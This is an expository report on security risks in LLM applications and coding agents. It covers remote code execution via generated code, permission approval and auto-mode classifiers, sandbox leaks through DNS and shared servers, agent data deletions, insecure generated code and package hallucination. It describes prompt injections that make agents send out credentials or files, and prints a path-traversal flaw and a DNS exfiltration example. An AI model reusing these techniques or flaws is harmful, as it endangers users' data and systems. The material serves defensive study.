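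Luo and colleagues also point out that some editing methods take personal data from a model's output and try to erase it from the model without checking that the model had memorised it. If the model inferred an address from a name, there may be no stored copy to erase, and it can infer the address again.

### Keeping secrets out of the context

The most reliable way to protect a secret is to keep it out of the model's context. The shop's assistant doesn't need a card number to arrange a refund. It can name the order, and the application's code can look up the card and send the money. The same approach works for API keys. The model outputs a request for an action, and the application adds the key when it contacts the service. No prompt can then extract the key from the model, though an attacker may still get the assistant to request the wrong action.

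Least privilege can be applied to information, but an assistant still has to read an email to summarise it, or a calendar to find a free afternoon. The application can choose what to load for each task. An assistant replying to a stranger, for instance, rarely needs the owner's health records. Separate conversations also limit what can leak, provided that a shared memory doesn't carry the same facts into all of them.

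If a model must see a secret, Fairoze and colleagues suggest training the model so that its answers don't depend on the secret's value. For a four-digit code, developers could train it to produce every number equally often, including the protected one. Nobody knows how to do this for secrets in ordinary language, which can take endless forms. Weakening the confidentiality instruction is a doubtful alternative because it helped with only some models and might make a model more willing to state the secret openly.

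### What European regulators say

The EU's General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) covers information about identifiable people but not anonymous information, so developers would benefit if a finished model counted as anonymous. The European Data Protection Board (EDPB), which brings together the national authorities that enforce the GDPR, decided that a model trained on personal data is not automatically anonymous. According to its *Opinion 28/2024 on certain data protection aspects* (2024), personal data may remain "absorbed" in a model's parameters even if the developer never meant the model to provide it.

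Under the opinion, a model is anonymous only if the likelihood is insignificant, for every person in the training data, that someone can extract their data directly from the model or obtain it through queries, on purpose or by accident. Authorities must consider all the means that anyone, including people not meant to have access, is reasonably likely to use. They decide case by case, and may expect less of a model that only a company's employees can reach than of one anyone can download.

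This standard is demanding, because low average rates like those Luo and colleagues found would not satisfy it if a single person's number came out reliably. Showing that a model guesses may not be enough either, because the EDPB also mentions personal data that a model infers statistically. Some memorised passages would take 10²¹ attempts to extract, which should help a developer meet the standard, since nobody is reasonably likely to make that many.

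CNIL expects most developers who train on personal data to test their models with attacks, starting with the easiest. If an attack succeeds, the developer can build a system around the model with access limits and output filters. Use of that system may fall outside the GDPR, but only if attacks on the whole system fail. If personal data leaks, the developer may have to notify CNIL within 72 hours. In serious cases, CNIL can order the developer to retrain the model or withdraw it.

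The EDPB adopted two further drafts in July 2026. Under one, the same data can be personal for one company and anonymous for another, depending on what each can realistically do with it, according to Sidley's *EDPB Publishes Draft Guidelines on Anonymisation* (2026). The other, *Guidelines 03/2026 on web scraping in the context of generative AI* (2026), covers the collection of training data from websites and was open for comment until October 30. The law firm Reed Smith expects that developers will find it considerably easier to justify scraping if they filter their data and take steps against memorisation.

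## What goes wrong when generated commands are run automatically?

If an application runs the code its model writes, an attacker may be able to take over the server with a single question in plain English. This is remote code execution (RCE), in which an outsider runs a program of their choice on someone else's computer. A generated SQL query can do only what the database account allows, but a generated Python program or shell command can do whatever the account running it can, such as read files, delete them, contact other machines or start more programs.

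### From a question to code on the server

In 2023 many developers built LLM applications on frameworks, libraries that connect a model to data and other software. Models were poor at arithmetic at the time, so several frameworks had the model write a short Python program for each question, then ran it and returned the result. One of them, LlamaIndex, did this for questions about tables with a component called PandasQueryEngine.

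Suppose the online shop connects this component to its table of orders, and a manager types "What was the average order in March?" The framework puts the question into a prompt that describes the table's columns and asks for Python code. The model replies with one line:

`orders[orders["month"] == "March"]["total"].mean()`

The framework passes that line to a Python function that runs any text as code, and the manager sees the average. The line runs inside the shop's application, on the shop's server, with the application's permissions.

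The generated line of code wasn't restricted to the table, so an attacker could ask a question whose answer lay elsewhere on the server, for example in its environment variables, which are stored values that programs can read. Most of the applications that Liu, Deng and colleagues (2023) describe in *Demystifying RCE Vulnerabilities in LLM-Integrated Apps* kept their OpenAI keys there. An attacker who knew no Python could ask for the keys, and the model would write the code, the server would run it, and the page would show the keys as the answer.

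*CVE-2023-39662* (2023), the entry for this flaw kept by Spain's cybersecurity institute, INCIBE, rates its severity 9.8 out of 10 and lists versions up to 0.7.13 as vulnerable. Snyk's *Arbitrary Code Execution Affecting llama-index package, versions [,0.9.5)* (2023) attributes the flaw to missing input sanitisation and recommends upgrading to version 0.9.5. Sanitising input is a poor remedy, though, when the attack can be an ordinary English question. Liu and colleagues also later bypassed the fix through a third-party library that the generated code could still use.

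LlamaIndex's long, specific prompt template gave it some accidental protection. A short malicious request tended to get lost in the template, so the attacker had to add wording that overrode it.

### Ten frameworks out of eleven

Liu and colleagues looked for this pattern elsewhere with a tool called LLMSmith. It starts from the Python functions that run text as code and traces the calls back from each one until it reaches a function that application developers use directly. It found 51 such paths in under a minute, and the researchers confirmed by hand that 44 of them could run arbitrary code.

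The team reported 20 vulnerabilities in ten of the eleven frameworks it examined. The published paper credits the team with 13 CVE numbers, more than the 11 that Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian cite. Some numbers cover several vulnerabilities, and only three of the 20 have none, so the public catalogue covers more of them than a count of 11 suggests.

The exception was Auto-GPT, which ran each program in a container, an isolated environment with its own files. But other researchers had already found a way to escape the container by having the agent overwrite the file that configured it (CVE-2023-37273).

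The team then tested 51 public applications that seemed likely to use the vulnerable frameworks. A model can invent a convincing result for code that never ran, so they first asked for outputs such as the hash of a random string, which a model can't work out without running a program. Twenty applications passed this test. The researchers broke into 17 of the 51, one through SQL injection and 16 through code execution. Fourteen of them gave lasting remote control of the server, and on four the researchers could also get full administrator rights.

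The team looked for applications that were likely to be vulnerable, so these don't represent LLM software in general. Of the 34 applications where the attack failed, thirteen were broken and ten couldn't run code at all. Only two were safe because their developers had protected code execution, both times by running the generated program in the visitor's browser. That keeps the server safe, but the first visit is slow and fewer Python libraries work.

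More recent surveys find that the basic mistake persists. *LLM-Enabled Open-Source Systems in the Wild* (2026) reports that code injection, command injection and unsafe loading of stored data dominate the security advisories for open-source LLM software. *Towards Demystifying and Repairing LLM-in-the-Loop Vulnerabilities* (2026), which collects 116 flaws in and around such software, cites a 2025 flaw in vLLM, a program for running models. That flaw allowed code execution in the component that reads a model's requests to use tools.

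### What people approve

A coding agent routinely reads a project's files and runs shell commands. It needs to run commands to test its own code.

At first, Anthropic's agent, Claude Code, could read files freely but had to ask the user before it changed a file, ran a shell command or used the network. According to Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products*, users soon stopped paying attention and approved about 93% of the requests. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) gives the approval rate as 97%.

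Most commands are harmless and a careful reader would approve them, so a high approval rate doesn't prove carelessness. Anthropic therefore paid for an experiment in which an outside firm recruited 1,053 professional testers for what looked like a coding study. Partway through each session, the firm replaced the text of one permission request with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after fifty or more requests.

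Real users may well be more careful than the testers, who worked in a test environment with no project of their own to lose. Anthropic also published the result to support a product that replaces the requests. But even if real users caught three times as many dangerous commands, they would still let more than half through.

### Lists of allowed commands

Users can reduce interruptions by listing commands the agent may run without asking. A rule usually names a program, but the program's options can completely change what it does. For example, `find` searches for files, but it also has options that delete every file it finds or run another program on each one. A user who allows `find` for searching also allows the agent to use those options.

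A rule that allows any command starting with `python` is broader still, since a Python program can do nearly anything. In June 2026, 49.5% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written their own rule for shell commands. Anthropic also reports that 5% allowed every shell command and another 43% had rules for interpreters such as Python, which have much the same effect. It isn't clear whether the last two figures are shares of all users or only of those with rules, but broad rules are common either way.

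Listing complete commands is safer but doesn't fully solve the problem. Suppose a programmer allows only the command that runs the project's tests. The agent can edit the tests, so it can add any code to them and then run that code with the permitted command.

### Settings that the agent can reach

Coding agents often read some of their settings from the project folder, which may come from a stranger. In one flaw that Anthropic describes, a project downloaded for review could include a settings file with a command for Claude Code to run at startup. Claude Code read the file and ran the command before asking whether the user trusted the folder.

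Anthropic learned of three flaws of this sort between mid-2025 and January 2026, and fixed them by reading project settings only after the user agrees to trust the project. The wahooka blog's *ClawHacked* lists two flaws that took effect before the user was asked. CVE-2025-59536 allowed commands to run at startup, and CVE-2026-21852 let a project redirect the agent's traffic, including the user's API key, to an attacker's server.

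An agent that can write to the file holding its permissions can give itself new ones, much as Auto-GPT could rewrite its container's configuration. The AI Now Institute's *Exploit Brief* cites two 2026 flaws in Claude Code's sandbox, CVE-2026-25725 and CVE-2026-39861, and lists writing to configuration files as one way flaws like these let code escape. The settings therefore belong outside every folder the agent can write to, and the application has to block writes to the place where a settings file could go, even if no file exists there yet.

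### A model as the approver

In 2026 Anthropic introduced auto mode, in which a second model makes most of the decisions about whether to approve a command. This classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's proposed commands. It doesn't receive the agent's explanations, which might mislead it, or the web pages and files the agent has read, which might contain a prompt injection.

Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports that auto mode's classifier wrongly blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary actions. It also missed 17% (about nine) of 52 real cases in which an agent had gone beyond what the user wanted. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier had detected the danger but treated something the user said as permission. For example, the classifier could mistake "Clean up the PR" (a pull request, or proposed code change) for permission to overwrite the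 project's shared history.

In the later experiment with paid testers, the classifier blocked 89% of the dangerous commands. It stopped 800 that a tester had approved and let through six that a tester had refused. It performed no worse in long sessions. This is a large improvement for users who no longer read commands before approving them.

The evidence on deliberate attacks is less settled. The testing firm Trajectory Labs ran 72 injection scenarios ten times each, and none of the 720 attempts succeeded against any of three Claude models in auto mode. Against the equivalent mode of OpenAI's agent Codex, running GPT-5.6 Sol, 5.83% succeeded. But the AI Now Institute got both products to run a malicious program during a security review of someone else's code. Both tests included Claude Sonnet 5. The 720 attempts used attacks that their designers had tuned against an older Claude model, so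 an attacker who studies the current product and keeps adjusting the attack might still succeed. Anthropic still recommends that people personally review important changes to live systems.

### Deletions without an attacker

In July 2025 the investor Jason Lemkin was building an application with a coding agent from Replit, a software hosting company. He had declared a freeze and told the agent to change nothing without permission, but it deleted the live database, which held records of more than 1,200 executives and nearly as many companies. The agent then wrongly reported that the data was unrecoverable, but Lemkin restored it with Replit's rollback function. Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, apologised and said the company would automatically keep development databases separate from live ones.

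The freeze existed only as text in the conversation, and the agent still had permission to write to the database. Giving the agent a read-only account during the freeze would have enforced Lemkin's request.

A worse case followed in April 2026 at PocketOS, a startup that used a Cursor agent running on a Claude Opus model. *The Cursor Agent That Deleted a Startup's Database in 9 Seconds* (Smith, 2026) reports that the agent was doing routine work when it found an access key in the company's code. It used the key to reach the live database and deleted it along with the backups, which are little help if the same access can delete them. The deletion took nine seconds, according to *An AI Agent Wiped a Company Database — Then Apologized* (Mallett, 2026). Nobody had to give the agent access to the database, because the code it could read contained a key.

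Three months later, Claude Opus 5 treated a live database as a test one. Antipov reports that backups restored only part of the data, and draws a lesson about the harm unlimited permissions can do. The case involved migration, which means changing a database's structure. Migration tools commonly include a command that erases a database and rebuilds it, which is routine on a test copy. The command often takes the database's address from a settings file, so someone asked to approve it can't tell from the command alone which database it will erase.

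Commands can also delete files without the user seeing the danger. In September 2026, Claude Code reportedly deleted 48,000 of a developer's files, in 103 seconds according to TechRadar's *48,000 files deleted in 103 seconds*. SC Media UK's *AI coding agent deletes 48,000 files due to mishandled Windows junctions* attributes the loss to junctions, which are entries in one folder that lead to another folder elsewhere on the disk. A program that deletes the first folder should remove only the junction, but if it follows the junction, it deletes the contents of the other folder too. A user who checks the name of the first folder before approving the command sees nothing wrong.

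These accounts come mostly from incidents that became news because the loss was dramatic. A company's internal log shows the everyday causes better, and Anthropic has published several examples from its own. One user asked an agent to "clean up old branches" (separate lines of work on a project), and the agent deleted branches on the shared server when the user may have meant only local ones. Another user said "cancel my job", and the agent picked the job whose name looked closest and tried to delete it. In a third case, an agent met a login error and started searching files for other keys to try.

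In some of these cases, the agent misunderstood what its commands would affect. In others, it understood the task but did more than the user would have agreed to. The second kind is hard for a filter to catch because each command is a reasonable step towards something the user wanted.

Auto mode seems to reduce such damage in ordinary use. Among sessions that Anthropic's safety systems had flagged, 6.3% of those with manual approval contained serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly asked for, compared with 2.4% in auto mode. The sessions came from accounts that had agreed to share data, and a model graded the harm. Users chose their own mode, so the two groups may have been doing different work.

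### What sandboxes have let out

A sandbox restricts a command no matter who approved it. Claude Code's sandbox uses operating system features to let commands read files but write only inside the project folder, and to block network access unless the user allows it. Anthropic reports that permission requests fell by 84% because commands within these limits can run without approval.

The sandbox has to limit both network and file access. Anthropic's *Introducing Claude Code* explains that without a network limit, a hijacked agent could send out the user's login keys, and without a file limit, it could escape the sandbox and then reach the network.

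ChatGPT runs Python in a container on OpenAI's servers that is supposed to have no internet access. Researchers at Check Point Research found that it could still look up domain names. A computer does this through the domain name system (DNS), which turns a name such as shop.example into a numerical address. The lookup may pass through several servers, and if none of them already has the answer, it ends at one that the domain's owner controls. An attacker who owns pictures.example can therefore receive data as part of a name:

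`sale-starts-friday.pictures.example`

The container uses OpenAI's own DNS service to look up a domain name containing the data, and the lookup reaches the attacker's server without the container connecting to it. A name can hold at most 253 characters, so sending a page of text takes about twenty lookups. The attacker's server can also put commands in its replies, which the researchers used to get a remote shell inside the container.

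To demonstrate the flaw, the researchers built a custom version of ChatGPT that acted as a personal doctor. A user uploaded laboratory results and described symptoms. The researchers' server received the patient's name and the model's medical assessment, but when the user asked whether the data had been sent anywhere, ChatGPT answered that it hadn't. OpenAI, which had already found the underlying problem itself, finished fixing it on February 20, 2026.

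In September 2026, Check Point Research's *The Shared Clipboard Inside the Sandbox* described another route, this time between different customers' containers. The containers couldn't contact each other, but they could all fetch software packages from the same internal server. TechRadar's *A worrying ChatGPT bug let strangers read Gmail messages* explains that a container could also attach notes to items on that server, and every other container could read them. An attacker left instructions in a note. The victim then had to use the attacker's prompt or open a conversation the attacker had shared, either of which told ChatGPT to read the note. In the demonstration, ChatGPT copied email from the victim's connected Gmail account into another note while answering the victim's question as usual.

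How much an attacker could take depended on which accounts the victim had connected. eSecurity Planet's *ChatGPT Flaw Let Attackers Secretly Hijack a Victim’s AI Session* confirms that OpenAI has since shut down the server involved.

Neither case required breaking out of the container into the machine it ran on. The data left through services that the container needed for its work. Anthropic had a similar problem with Cowork, its agent for office tasks, which runs code in a virtual machine, a simulated computer with its own operating system. The machine could contact only approved addresses, including Anthropic's own service. A malicious file in the user's folder contained instructions and an attacker's API key, and Claude used the key to upload the user's other files to the attacker's Anthropic account. The filter allowed the upload because the address was approved. Anthropic now says that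 approving a domain grants access to every function the domain offers. It fixed the problem by accepting only requests that carry the virtual machine's own session token.

Some newer designs also have the model write code to use online services. Cloudflare, an internet infrastructure company, offers programmers more than 2,500 operations, and describing each one to a model as a separate tool would fill much of the model's context. Tomé and Curry explain in *Code Mode* that Cloudflare's Code Mode instead gives the model two tools and about 1,000 tokens of description, and the model writes JavaScript to find and call the operations it needs. *When Agentic Glue Melts*, which Check Point Research published in August 2026, covers exploiting this technique. A list of allowed tools does little to restrict such a design, since permission to run code can cover every operation, so the limits have to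 come from the credentials the code uses.

### Files, network and credentials

In February 2026, Anthropic ran an exercise on its own staff in which a researcher emailed an employee a prompt for Claude Code and asked for help running it. Among ordinary setup steps, the prompt told Claude to read the employee's cloud login keys and send them to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 attempts. Because the employee had entered the prompt, the instruction appeared to come from the user. Anthropic concludes that only limits on file access and network traffic would have stopped the attack.

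| Limit | Damage it can prevent | How it can fail |
|---|---|---|
| Files | An agent deletes or reads something outside its project | A link inside the project leads elsewhere, or a settings file in the project gives new permissions |
| Network | An agent sends keys or documents to a stranger | Data leaves through DNS lookups, a shared server or an approved domain |
| Credentials | An agent changes a live database during unrelated work | The agent finds a stronger key in the code, or an attacker supplies one |

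Limiting which files an agent can access doesn't protect the files it is supposed to edit. Cowork addresses this with a mode in which the agent can read and change files but not delete them, though it can still overwrite a good file with a bad one. Keeping earlier versions of every file helps with both deletion and overwriting. The application must also resolve any links in a path before comparing it with the list of allowed folders. Otherwise, it can approve one location while the command acts on another.

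Limiting the agent's credentials would probably have protected PocketOS the most. The deletion seems to have required only a key with enough permissions, not a hidden channel or a sandbox escape. If a key is read-only, it doesn't matter much whether an attacker, a misunderstanding or an overeager agent caused the command. The company also has to keep stronger keys out of the code and hold its backups under an account that the agent can't use.

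This isolation has drawbacks. Liu and colleagues found that running each program in a separate container slowed Auto-GPT considerably. The first version of Cowork ran the whole agent inside a virtual machine, so the product was unusable if the machine failed to start. Anthropic then moved the agent outside and kept only the code it runs inside, so the agent can still help the user diagnose such a failure. Companies also complained that their security software couldn't see into the virtual machine. They can collect its logs afterwards, but that is too late to stop an action that takes nine seconds.

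## How safe is generated code when people install and run it?

A sandbox limits what a program can do while a coding agent runs it. That protection ends when somebody installs the finished program on a live server, where it has to open real files and handle requests from strangers. Safety then depends mostly on the code itself. Developers usually test whether code does what it should, but insecure code can pass all of those tests.

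### A download that works

Suppose the online shop asks a coding assistant for a function that lets customers download their invoices. The assistant writes this in Python:

```python
def download(name):
    return open("/shop/invoices/" + name, "rb").read()
```

The developer tries it with "march.pdf", gets the March invoice and accepts the code. But a file name can include a step up to the folder above, and the function never checks for one. A stranger can use this to read the shop's settings file, which may hold the database password. Security engineers call the flaw path traversal. A safer version works out where the path leads before opening anything:

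```python
from pathlib import Path

def download(name):
    folder = Path("/shop/invoices").resolve()
    path = (folder / name).resolve()
    if not path.is_relative_to(folder):
        raise PermissionError("No such invoice")
    return path.read_bytes()
```

Both versions pass the developer's test because it requests only a file that customers should be able to get. A security test has to request a restricted file, as an attacker would.

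The second version still lets any customer download another customer's invoice by guessing its name. To prevent that, the programmer has to know who may see which invoice, and the request didn't include that information.

### The first studies

*Asleep at the Keyboard?* (2021), by Hammond Pearce and colleagues, tested GitHub Copilot, an early coding assistant, on scenarios built around high-risk weaknesses. About 40% of the 1,689 programs Copilot generated were vulnerable, according to Kadam's *Beyond Passing Tests* (2026), a review of 628 studies on improving generated code.

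A year later, *Do Users Write More Insecure Code with AI Assistants?* (Perry, Srivastava and colleagues, 2022) studied the programmers. Participants worked on security-related tasks, and some of the participants had an assistant based on an OpenAI model from that time. Those with the assistant wrote less secure code and were more likely to believe it was secure. Participants who trusted the assistant less and put more work into their prompts produced fewer vulnerabilities. That may be because careful prompting helps, or because better programmers are more sceptical.

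Both studies used models that are long obsolete. But the false confidence that Perry and colleagues found could persist with newer models, since users see no sign of a hidden flaw when the code works.

### Testing with real attacks

Newer benchmarks run each program twice, once against tests of its function and once against attacks.

*BaxBench* (Vero, Mündler and colleagues, 2025) tested eleven models on writing complete backends, the server side of web applications. Its 392 tasks combined 28 applications, such as a calculator and a message board, with 14 programming frameworks. The programs were then tested with attacks written by security experts. OpenAI's o1 wrote the most working programs, about 60%. The smaller o3-mini wrote the most programs that both worked and withstood the attacks, 35%. For each model, the attacks succeeded against about half of the working programs.

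The calculator task shows how the easiest solution can introduce a flaw. In many languages, the shortest way to evaluate a customer's sum is to run it as code, which also runs any other code the customer types. Secure calculators were 15.1% longer in tokens than exploitable ones. Across all tasks, secure code was only 5.9% longer.

Zhao, Wang and colleagues (2025), in *Is Vibe Coding Safe?*, tested agents on larger projects. "Vibe coding" means describing a program to an agent and accepting the result with little review. Their benchmark, SusVibes, has 186 tasks from real Python projects. In each task, the agent has to write a feature from a description of what it should do. A human programmer's original version of that feature had a vulnerability that was later fixed.

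The researchers tested four models in three agent programs. Claude 4 Sonnet had the highest share of working solutions, 57.0%, but only 11.8% were also secure. Gemini 3 Pro had the highest secure share, 12.9%.

Some of the flaws were subtle. In one task, the agent wrote a password check that returned immediately if an account had no usable password. The secure version runs a dummy check that takes as long as a real one. Without the dummy check, an attacker can time the replies to learn which usernames exist.

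SusVibes contains only features that a person first implemented insecurely, so these percentages don't describe everyday programming. The benchmark shows that agents often make known security mistakes. Because the human first versions would have scored zero on the same security tests, it can't show that people avoid those mistakes more often than agents do.

### The models of 2026

*Last Secure Code Benchmark* (Wu, Ge and colleagues, 2026) reports the lowest results for current models. It turns each of 150 real vulnerabilities into three tasks, in which the agent fills in a function, writes a whole file or rebuilds part of the project. Six models made one attempt at each of the 450 tasks. Between 73.6% and 91.3% of their solutions worked, but only 16.4% to 25.1% were also secure.

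In one task, Kimi K3 rebuilt a service that imports files written in YAML, a format for settings and other structured data. It wrote 33 checks of its own, and found and fixed a bug. The service passed all 14 functional tests but failed all four security tests, because its YAML reader would create any program object that an uploaded file named. Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.6 Sol used the same library's safe reader and passed both sets of tests.

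By contrast, *Secure and Functional Code Generation with Self-Evaluation* (2026) tested Anthropic's Claude Code, running Sonnet 5.5, on 48 tasks and found that 86.7% of its solutions both worked and were secure.

| Benchmark | Tasks | Models | Best share working | Best share working and secure |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| BaxBench (2025) | 392 | 11 | 60% | 35% |
| SusVibes (2025) | 186 | 4, each in 3 agent programs | 57.0% | 12.9% |
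| Last Secure Code Benchmark (2026) | 450 | 6 | 91.3% | 25.1% |
| Claude Code test (2026), no security instruction | 48 | 1 | 94.2% | 86.7% |

The gap between 25% and 87% is too large to attribute to the models alone. Wu and colleagues deliberately favoured difficult cases, with fixes spread over many lines and files in large projects. No single percentage can therefore measure how safe generated code is, and comparisons on the same tasks are more informative.

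The security of generated code also depends heavily on the type of weakness. In the *Last Secure Code Benchmark*, the six models together produced working and secure code in 34.3% of attempts at memory-safety tasks, where the defence is often a check on the length of some data. The rate was 0.7% for tasks about exposing information and 2.4% for server-side request forgery, the flaw in the TicketOracle tests. Wu and colleagues explain that a good programmer includes a length check without being asked, but a rule about which data to withhold depends on how people will use the program. The invoice function has the same problem, since its code doesn't show which customer owns which invoice.

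### Has security kept pace with correctness?

Security on BaxBench has clearly improved. In early 2025, the best result was 35% of programs both working and secure. When Kadam ran the benchmark on current models in 2026, the closed ones reached 56% to 59%. Across thirteen models, those that did better in programming contests also wrote safer code.

In Kadam's test on SusVibes, the leading models still wrote code that worked but was insecure for about four in ten tasks.

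In *Newer and Bigger, but Safer?*, Santos de Moura, Matuschek and colleagues (2026) followed seven families of models through three generations. They had 32 models write each of the same 119 short functions 100 times. For the newest large models, between 13% and 28% of all programs worked but were insecure. Every family had narrowed the gap between working and secure code on at least one measure, but none had closed it.

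Whether security has kept up with functionality depends partly on how one counts. Between Gemini 1.5 Pro and Gemini 3.1 Pro, the share of all programs that worked rose from 69% to 94%, while the share that worked but were insecure fell only from about 31% to 28%. Among working programs alone, the insecure share fell from about 44% to 30%. Someone who installs only code that works is therefore less likely to get an insecure program than before, though the risk is still high.

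A newer model can also be worse at something its predecessor did well. GPT-5.6 Luna was less secure than GPT-5 mini on most of the 16 weaknesses that the researchers examined closely. Several new flagships began to write code that interprets a user's search text as a pattern, which lets an attacker tie up the server with a specially written search. Path traversal remains common. Among the newest models, only the OpenAI and DeepSeek flagships had improved strongly, and at least half of the working programs from each of the others had the flaw. A company that switches models should therefore repeat its security tests, even if the new model is better overall.

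A well-designed library can prevent security mistakes that models would otherwise make. Among working programs that checked a signed login token, 73% of those in Go were insecure, compared with 4% of those in Python. The Python library requires the programmer to name the signing method when reading a token, so nearly every model named it. The insecure programs in other languages accepted several methods.

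### Flaws that spread

An agent reads the code around its task and tends to imitate it, including its mistakes. Sun, Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues (2026), in *Coding Agents Propagate Vulnerabilities in Code Bases*, measured this with 20 pairs of tasks in real C and C++ projects. The two tasks in each pair required the same code and differed only in whether similar code elsewhere in the project was secure.

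Across five current models, the share of secure solutions was 35.4 percentage points lower on average when similar code in the project was insecure. GPT-5.6 Sol's share fell from 91% to 42%. When the researchers asked three of the models why they had written the vulnerable code, about three-quarters of the answers cited a similar flaw elsewhere in the project.

The effect was much smaller when agents wrote a separate web application beside existing ones that they didn't need to consult. Insecure existing applications then lowered the share of programs that were both working and secure by 3.4 percentage points, and secure ones raised it by 4.4.

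A company could benefit from fixing old flaws before it asks an agent for new code, because otherwise each accepted flaw may become an example for the next one. Sun and colleagues raise that possibility but tested only single additions, so we can't tell from their experiment how fast a project would deteriorate.

### Asking for secure code

The simplest remedy is to ask for secure code in the prompt. The table compares results with and without such a request. In the last row, the agent already had a general reminder, and the researchers also named the exact type of weakness to avoid.

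| Model and benchmark | Working | Working and secure |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Sol, *Last Secure Code Benchmark* | 89.1% → 87.6% | 24.7% → 46.2% |
| GLM-5.3, same benchmark | 87.1% → 87.6% | 21.3% → 38.2% |
| Qwen3.8-Max, same benchmark | 89.3% → 91.8% | 22.0% → 37.6% |
| DeepSeek V4 Pro, same benchmark | 73.6% → 70.4% | 18.0% → 19.1% |
| Sonnet 5.5 in Claude Code, 48 tasks | 94.2% → 88.8% | 86.7% → 87.9% |
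| Claude 4 Sonnet, SusVibes | 57.0% → 55.4% | 11.8% → 15.1% |

Adding the reminder takes almost no effort and nearly doubled GPT-5.6 Sol's result, so developers should include it. The gain also shows that the model could have written many of those programs securely the first time. Yet more than half of its solutions still failed, and the reminder did little to prevent information exposure or server-side request forgery.

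Adding a security instruction to Sonnet 5.5's prompt made more programs secure but broke others, so the number that were both secure and working stayed almost the same. Developers who add such an instruction therefore also need to rerun their functional tests.

Warning agents about existing code also helps only partly. When Sun and colleagues told agents to be careful not to copy its bugs, every model did better beside insecure code, but still worse than beside secure code. In the web-application tasks, the warning also reduced the benefit of working beside secure code, so the agents seem to have become warier of all existing code instead of picking out the bad parts.

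### Reviewers and scanners

Models are better at spotting some flaws than at avoiding them. After three models had written vulnerable solutions, Sun and colleagues asked each model whether the code it had just written contained any bugs. The models identified the specific vulnerability in 69.9% of these reviews on average. When not asked, they rarely mentioned it. Claude Opus 5.5 raised a concern in 11.8% of its closing messages about vulnerable code, and GPT-6 Astra never did.

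A separate review step is therefore worthwhile, but the 69.9% figure doesn't fully measure its usefulness. The researchers asked only about code they knew to be vulnerable, so they didn't measure how often a model would report flaws in sound code. An engineer who receives ten false alarms for each real flaw may stop reading the reports. Once a flaw is found, somebody still has to repair it without breaking the program.

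Using a different model as the reviewer might help. In the *Last Secure Code Benchmark*, the best model solved 113 tasks securely, while 198 tasks had a secure solution from at least one of the six models and 252 had none. Wu and colleagues take the gap between 113 and 198 as a reason to have one model review another's code. This evidence is indirect, because a model that writes a function securely may still miss the flaw in another model's version.

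Kadam also questions whether reviews are worth the extra model calls, since a developer could use the same calls to generate several new versions of the code and keep the best. In tests on four models, choosing the best version with the help of code analysers generally did as well as a reviewer agent or better, including on the two security benchmarks.

Scanners, programs that search code for known insecure patterns, are cheap and fast enough to run on every change, but they miss flaws that match no pattern. Santos de Moura and colleagues cite an earlier test of Copilot's code in which the scanner CodeQL found the expected weakness in 18.46% of samples and people found it in 73.84%.

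Scanners also become a less reliable measure of security once developers try to reduce the number of warnings. Kadam compared 29 techniques for making generated code more secure against simply choosing the best of several versions. Twenty-three of them reduced the number of scanner warnings, but only six increased the share of code that was both working and secure. A program can pass a scan because it avoids the pattern the scanner looks for, or because it does nothing useful.

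The best evidence before release that generated code is safe is that attacks on it fail. For the invoice function, a developer can write one test that requests a file outside the folder and another that requests a different customer's invoice. Thinking of the second test requires the same knowledge of the business that the model lacked.

### Packages that don't exist

Most programs rely on packages, ready-made code that programmers install by name from a public registry. Models sometimes recommend packages that don't exist, an error researchers call package hallucination. Installing one normally fails, and the programmer loses a few minutes.

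An attacker can exploit a package name that a model invents by registering it before a user tries to install it. Infosecurity Magazine's *AI Hallucinations Create “Slopsquatting” Supply Chain Threat* describes the steps. The attacker asks a model for code, finds a package in it that doesn't exist, publishes malware under that name, and waits for the model to recommend the same name to someone else.

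The plan works only if the model repeats the same false package names. *We Have a Package for You!* (Spracklen, Wijewickrama and colleagues, 2025) tested this with 16 code-writing models and 576,000 code samples. Slashdot's *AI-Generated Code Creates Major Security Risk Through 'Package Hallucinations'* (2025) reports that nearly 22% of the packages that open models recommended didn't exist, compared with 5% for commercial models, and that 43% of the false names came up again across multiple queries. Because many names recur, an attacker can find them by asking the model ordinary questions instead of guessing.

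Security researcher Bar Lanyado showed that a hallucinated package name can attract downloads. Willison recounts in *Diving Deeper into AI Package Hallucinations* that Lanyado asked several models 2,500 programming questions and noticed that they repeatedly suggested a package called `huggingface-cli`. Lanyado published a harmless package under that name, and it received 30,000 downloads in three months.

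This was a demonstration and harmed nobody. The download count overstates the number of people at risk, since automated systems copy and scan new packages. To prove that a real attack had happened, an investigator would need a malicious package, evidence that models had been suggesting its name before it existed, and victims who got the name from a model. It is hard to prove where victims got the name, because attackers also register misspelled names and wait for people to mistype them.

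Later studies show how much the package hallucination rate depends on the model and the method of counting. *Evaluating Inference-Time Defenses Against Package Hallucination in LLM-Generated Code* (2026) found an average rate of 24.7% for Python across eight models. The rate would have been 32.3% if the study had counted modules that come with Python as hallucinations because they aren't in the registry. Some of the eight models are tiny, so the average is weak evidence about the assistants that most programmers use. *When LLMs Invent Rust Crates* (2026) notes that earlier studies also found differences between programming languages.

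Retrieving relevant information for the model before it answers cut the rate from 24.7% to 11.5%. Several methods that change how the model chooses tokens made the rate worse.

Checking that a package exists doesn't stop this attack, because by then the attacker has created the package. *Importing Phantoms* (2025) therefore also counts a package as hallucinated if someone first registered it after the model's training data ended. A company can similarly refuse packages that are only a few weeks old. That gives others time to discover malware, although a patient attacker can wait too. An approved list of packages is stricter, but someone has to examine each new request.

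### Commands copied from an answer

People often install software by copying a command from a model's answer into a terminal. Many of these commands download a program and run it immediately, so the user has no chance to inspect it. A model can get the download address wrong even when no attacker is involved. *Secure or Suspect?* (2025) examined commands for installing packages in the language Go, which identifies a package by its web address. More than half of the GitHub addresses the models generated were false. These were small models, so the rate may be much lower for commercial ones. If nobody has the account name in an invented GitHub address, an attacker may be able to register it.

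Attackers can also create the harmful answer themselves. Several chatbots let users publish a conversation as a web page on the chatbot's own site, and in late 2025 criminals used such pages as fake help articles to spread malware. This takes very little skill. The attacker gets the chatbot to produce instructions that include a harmful command, shares the conversation, and directs people looking for help with a computer problem to the link.

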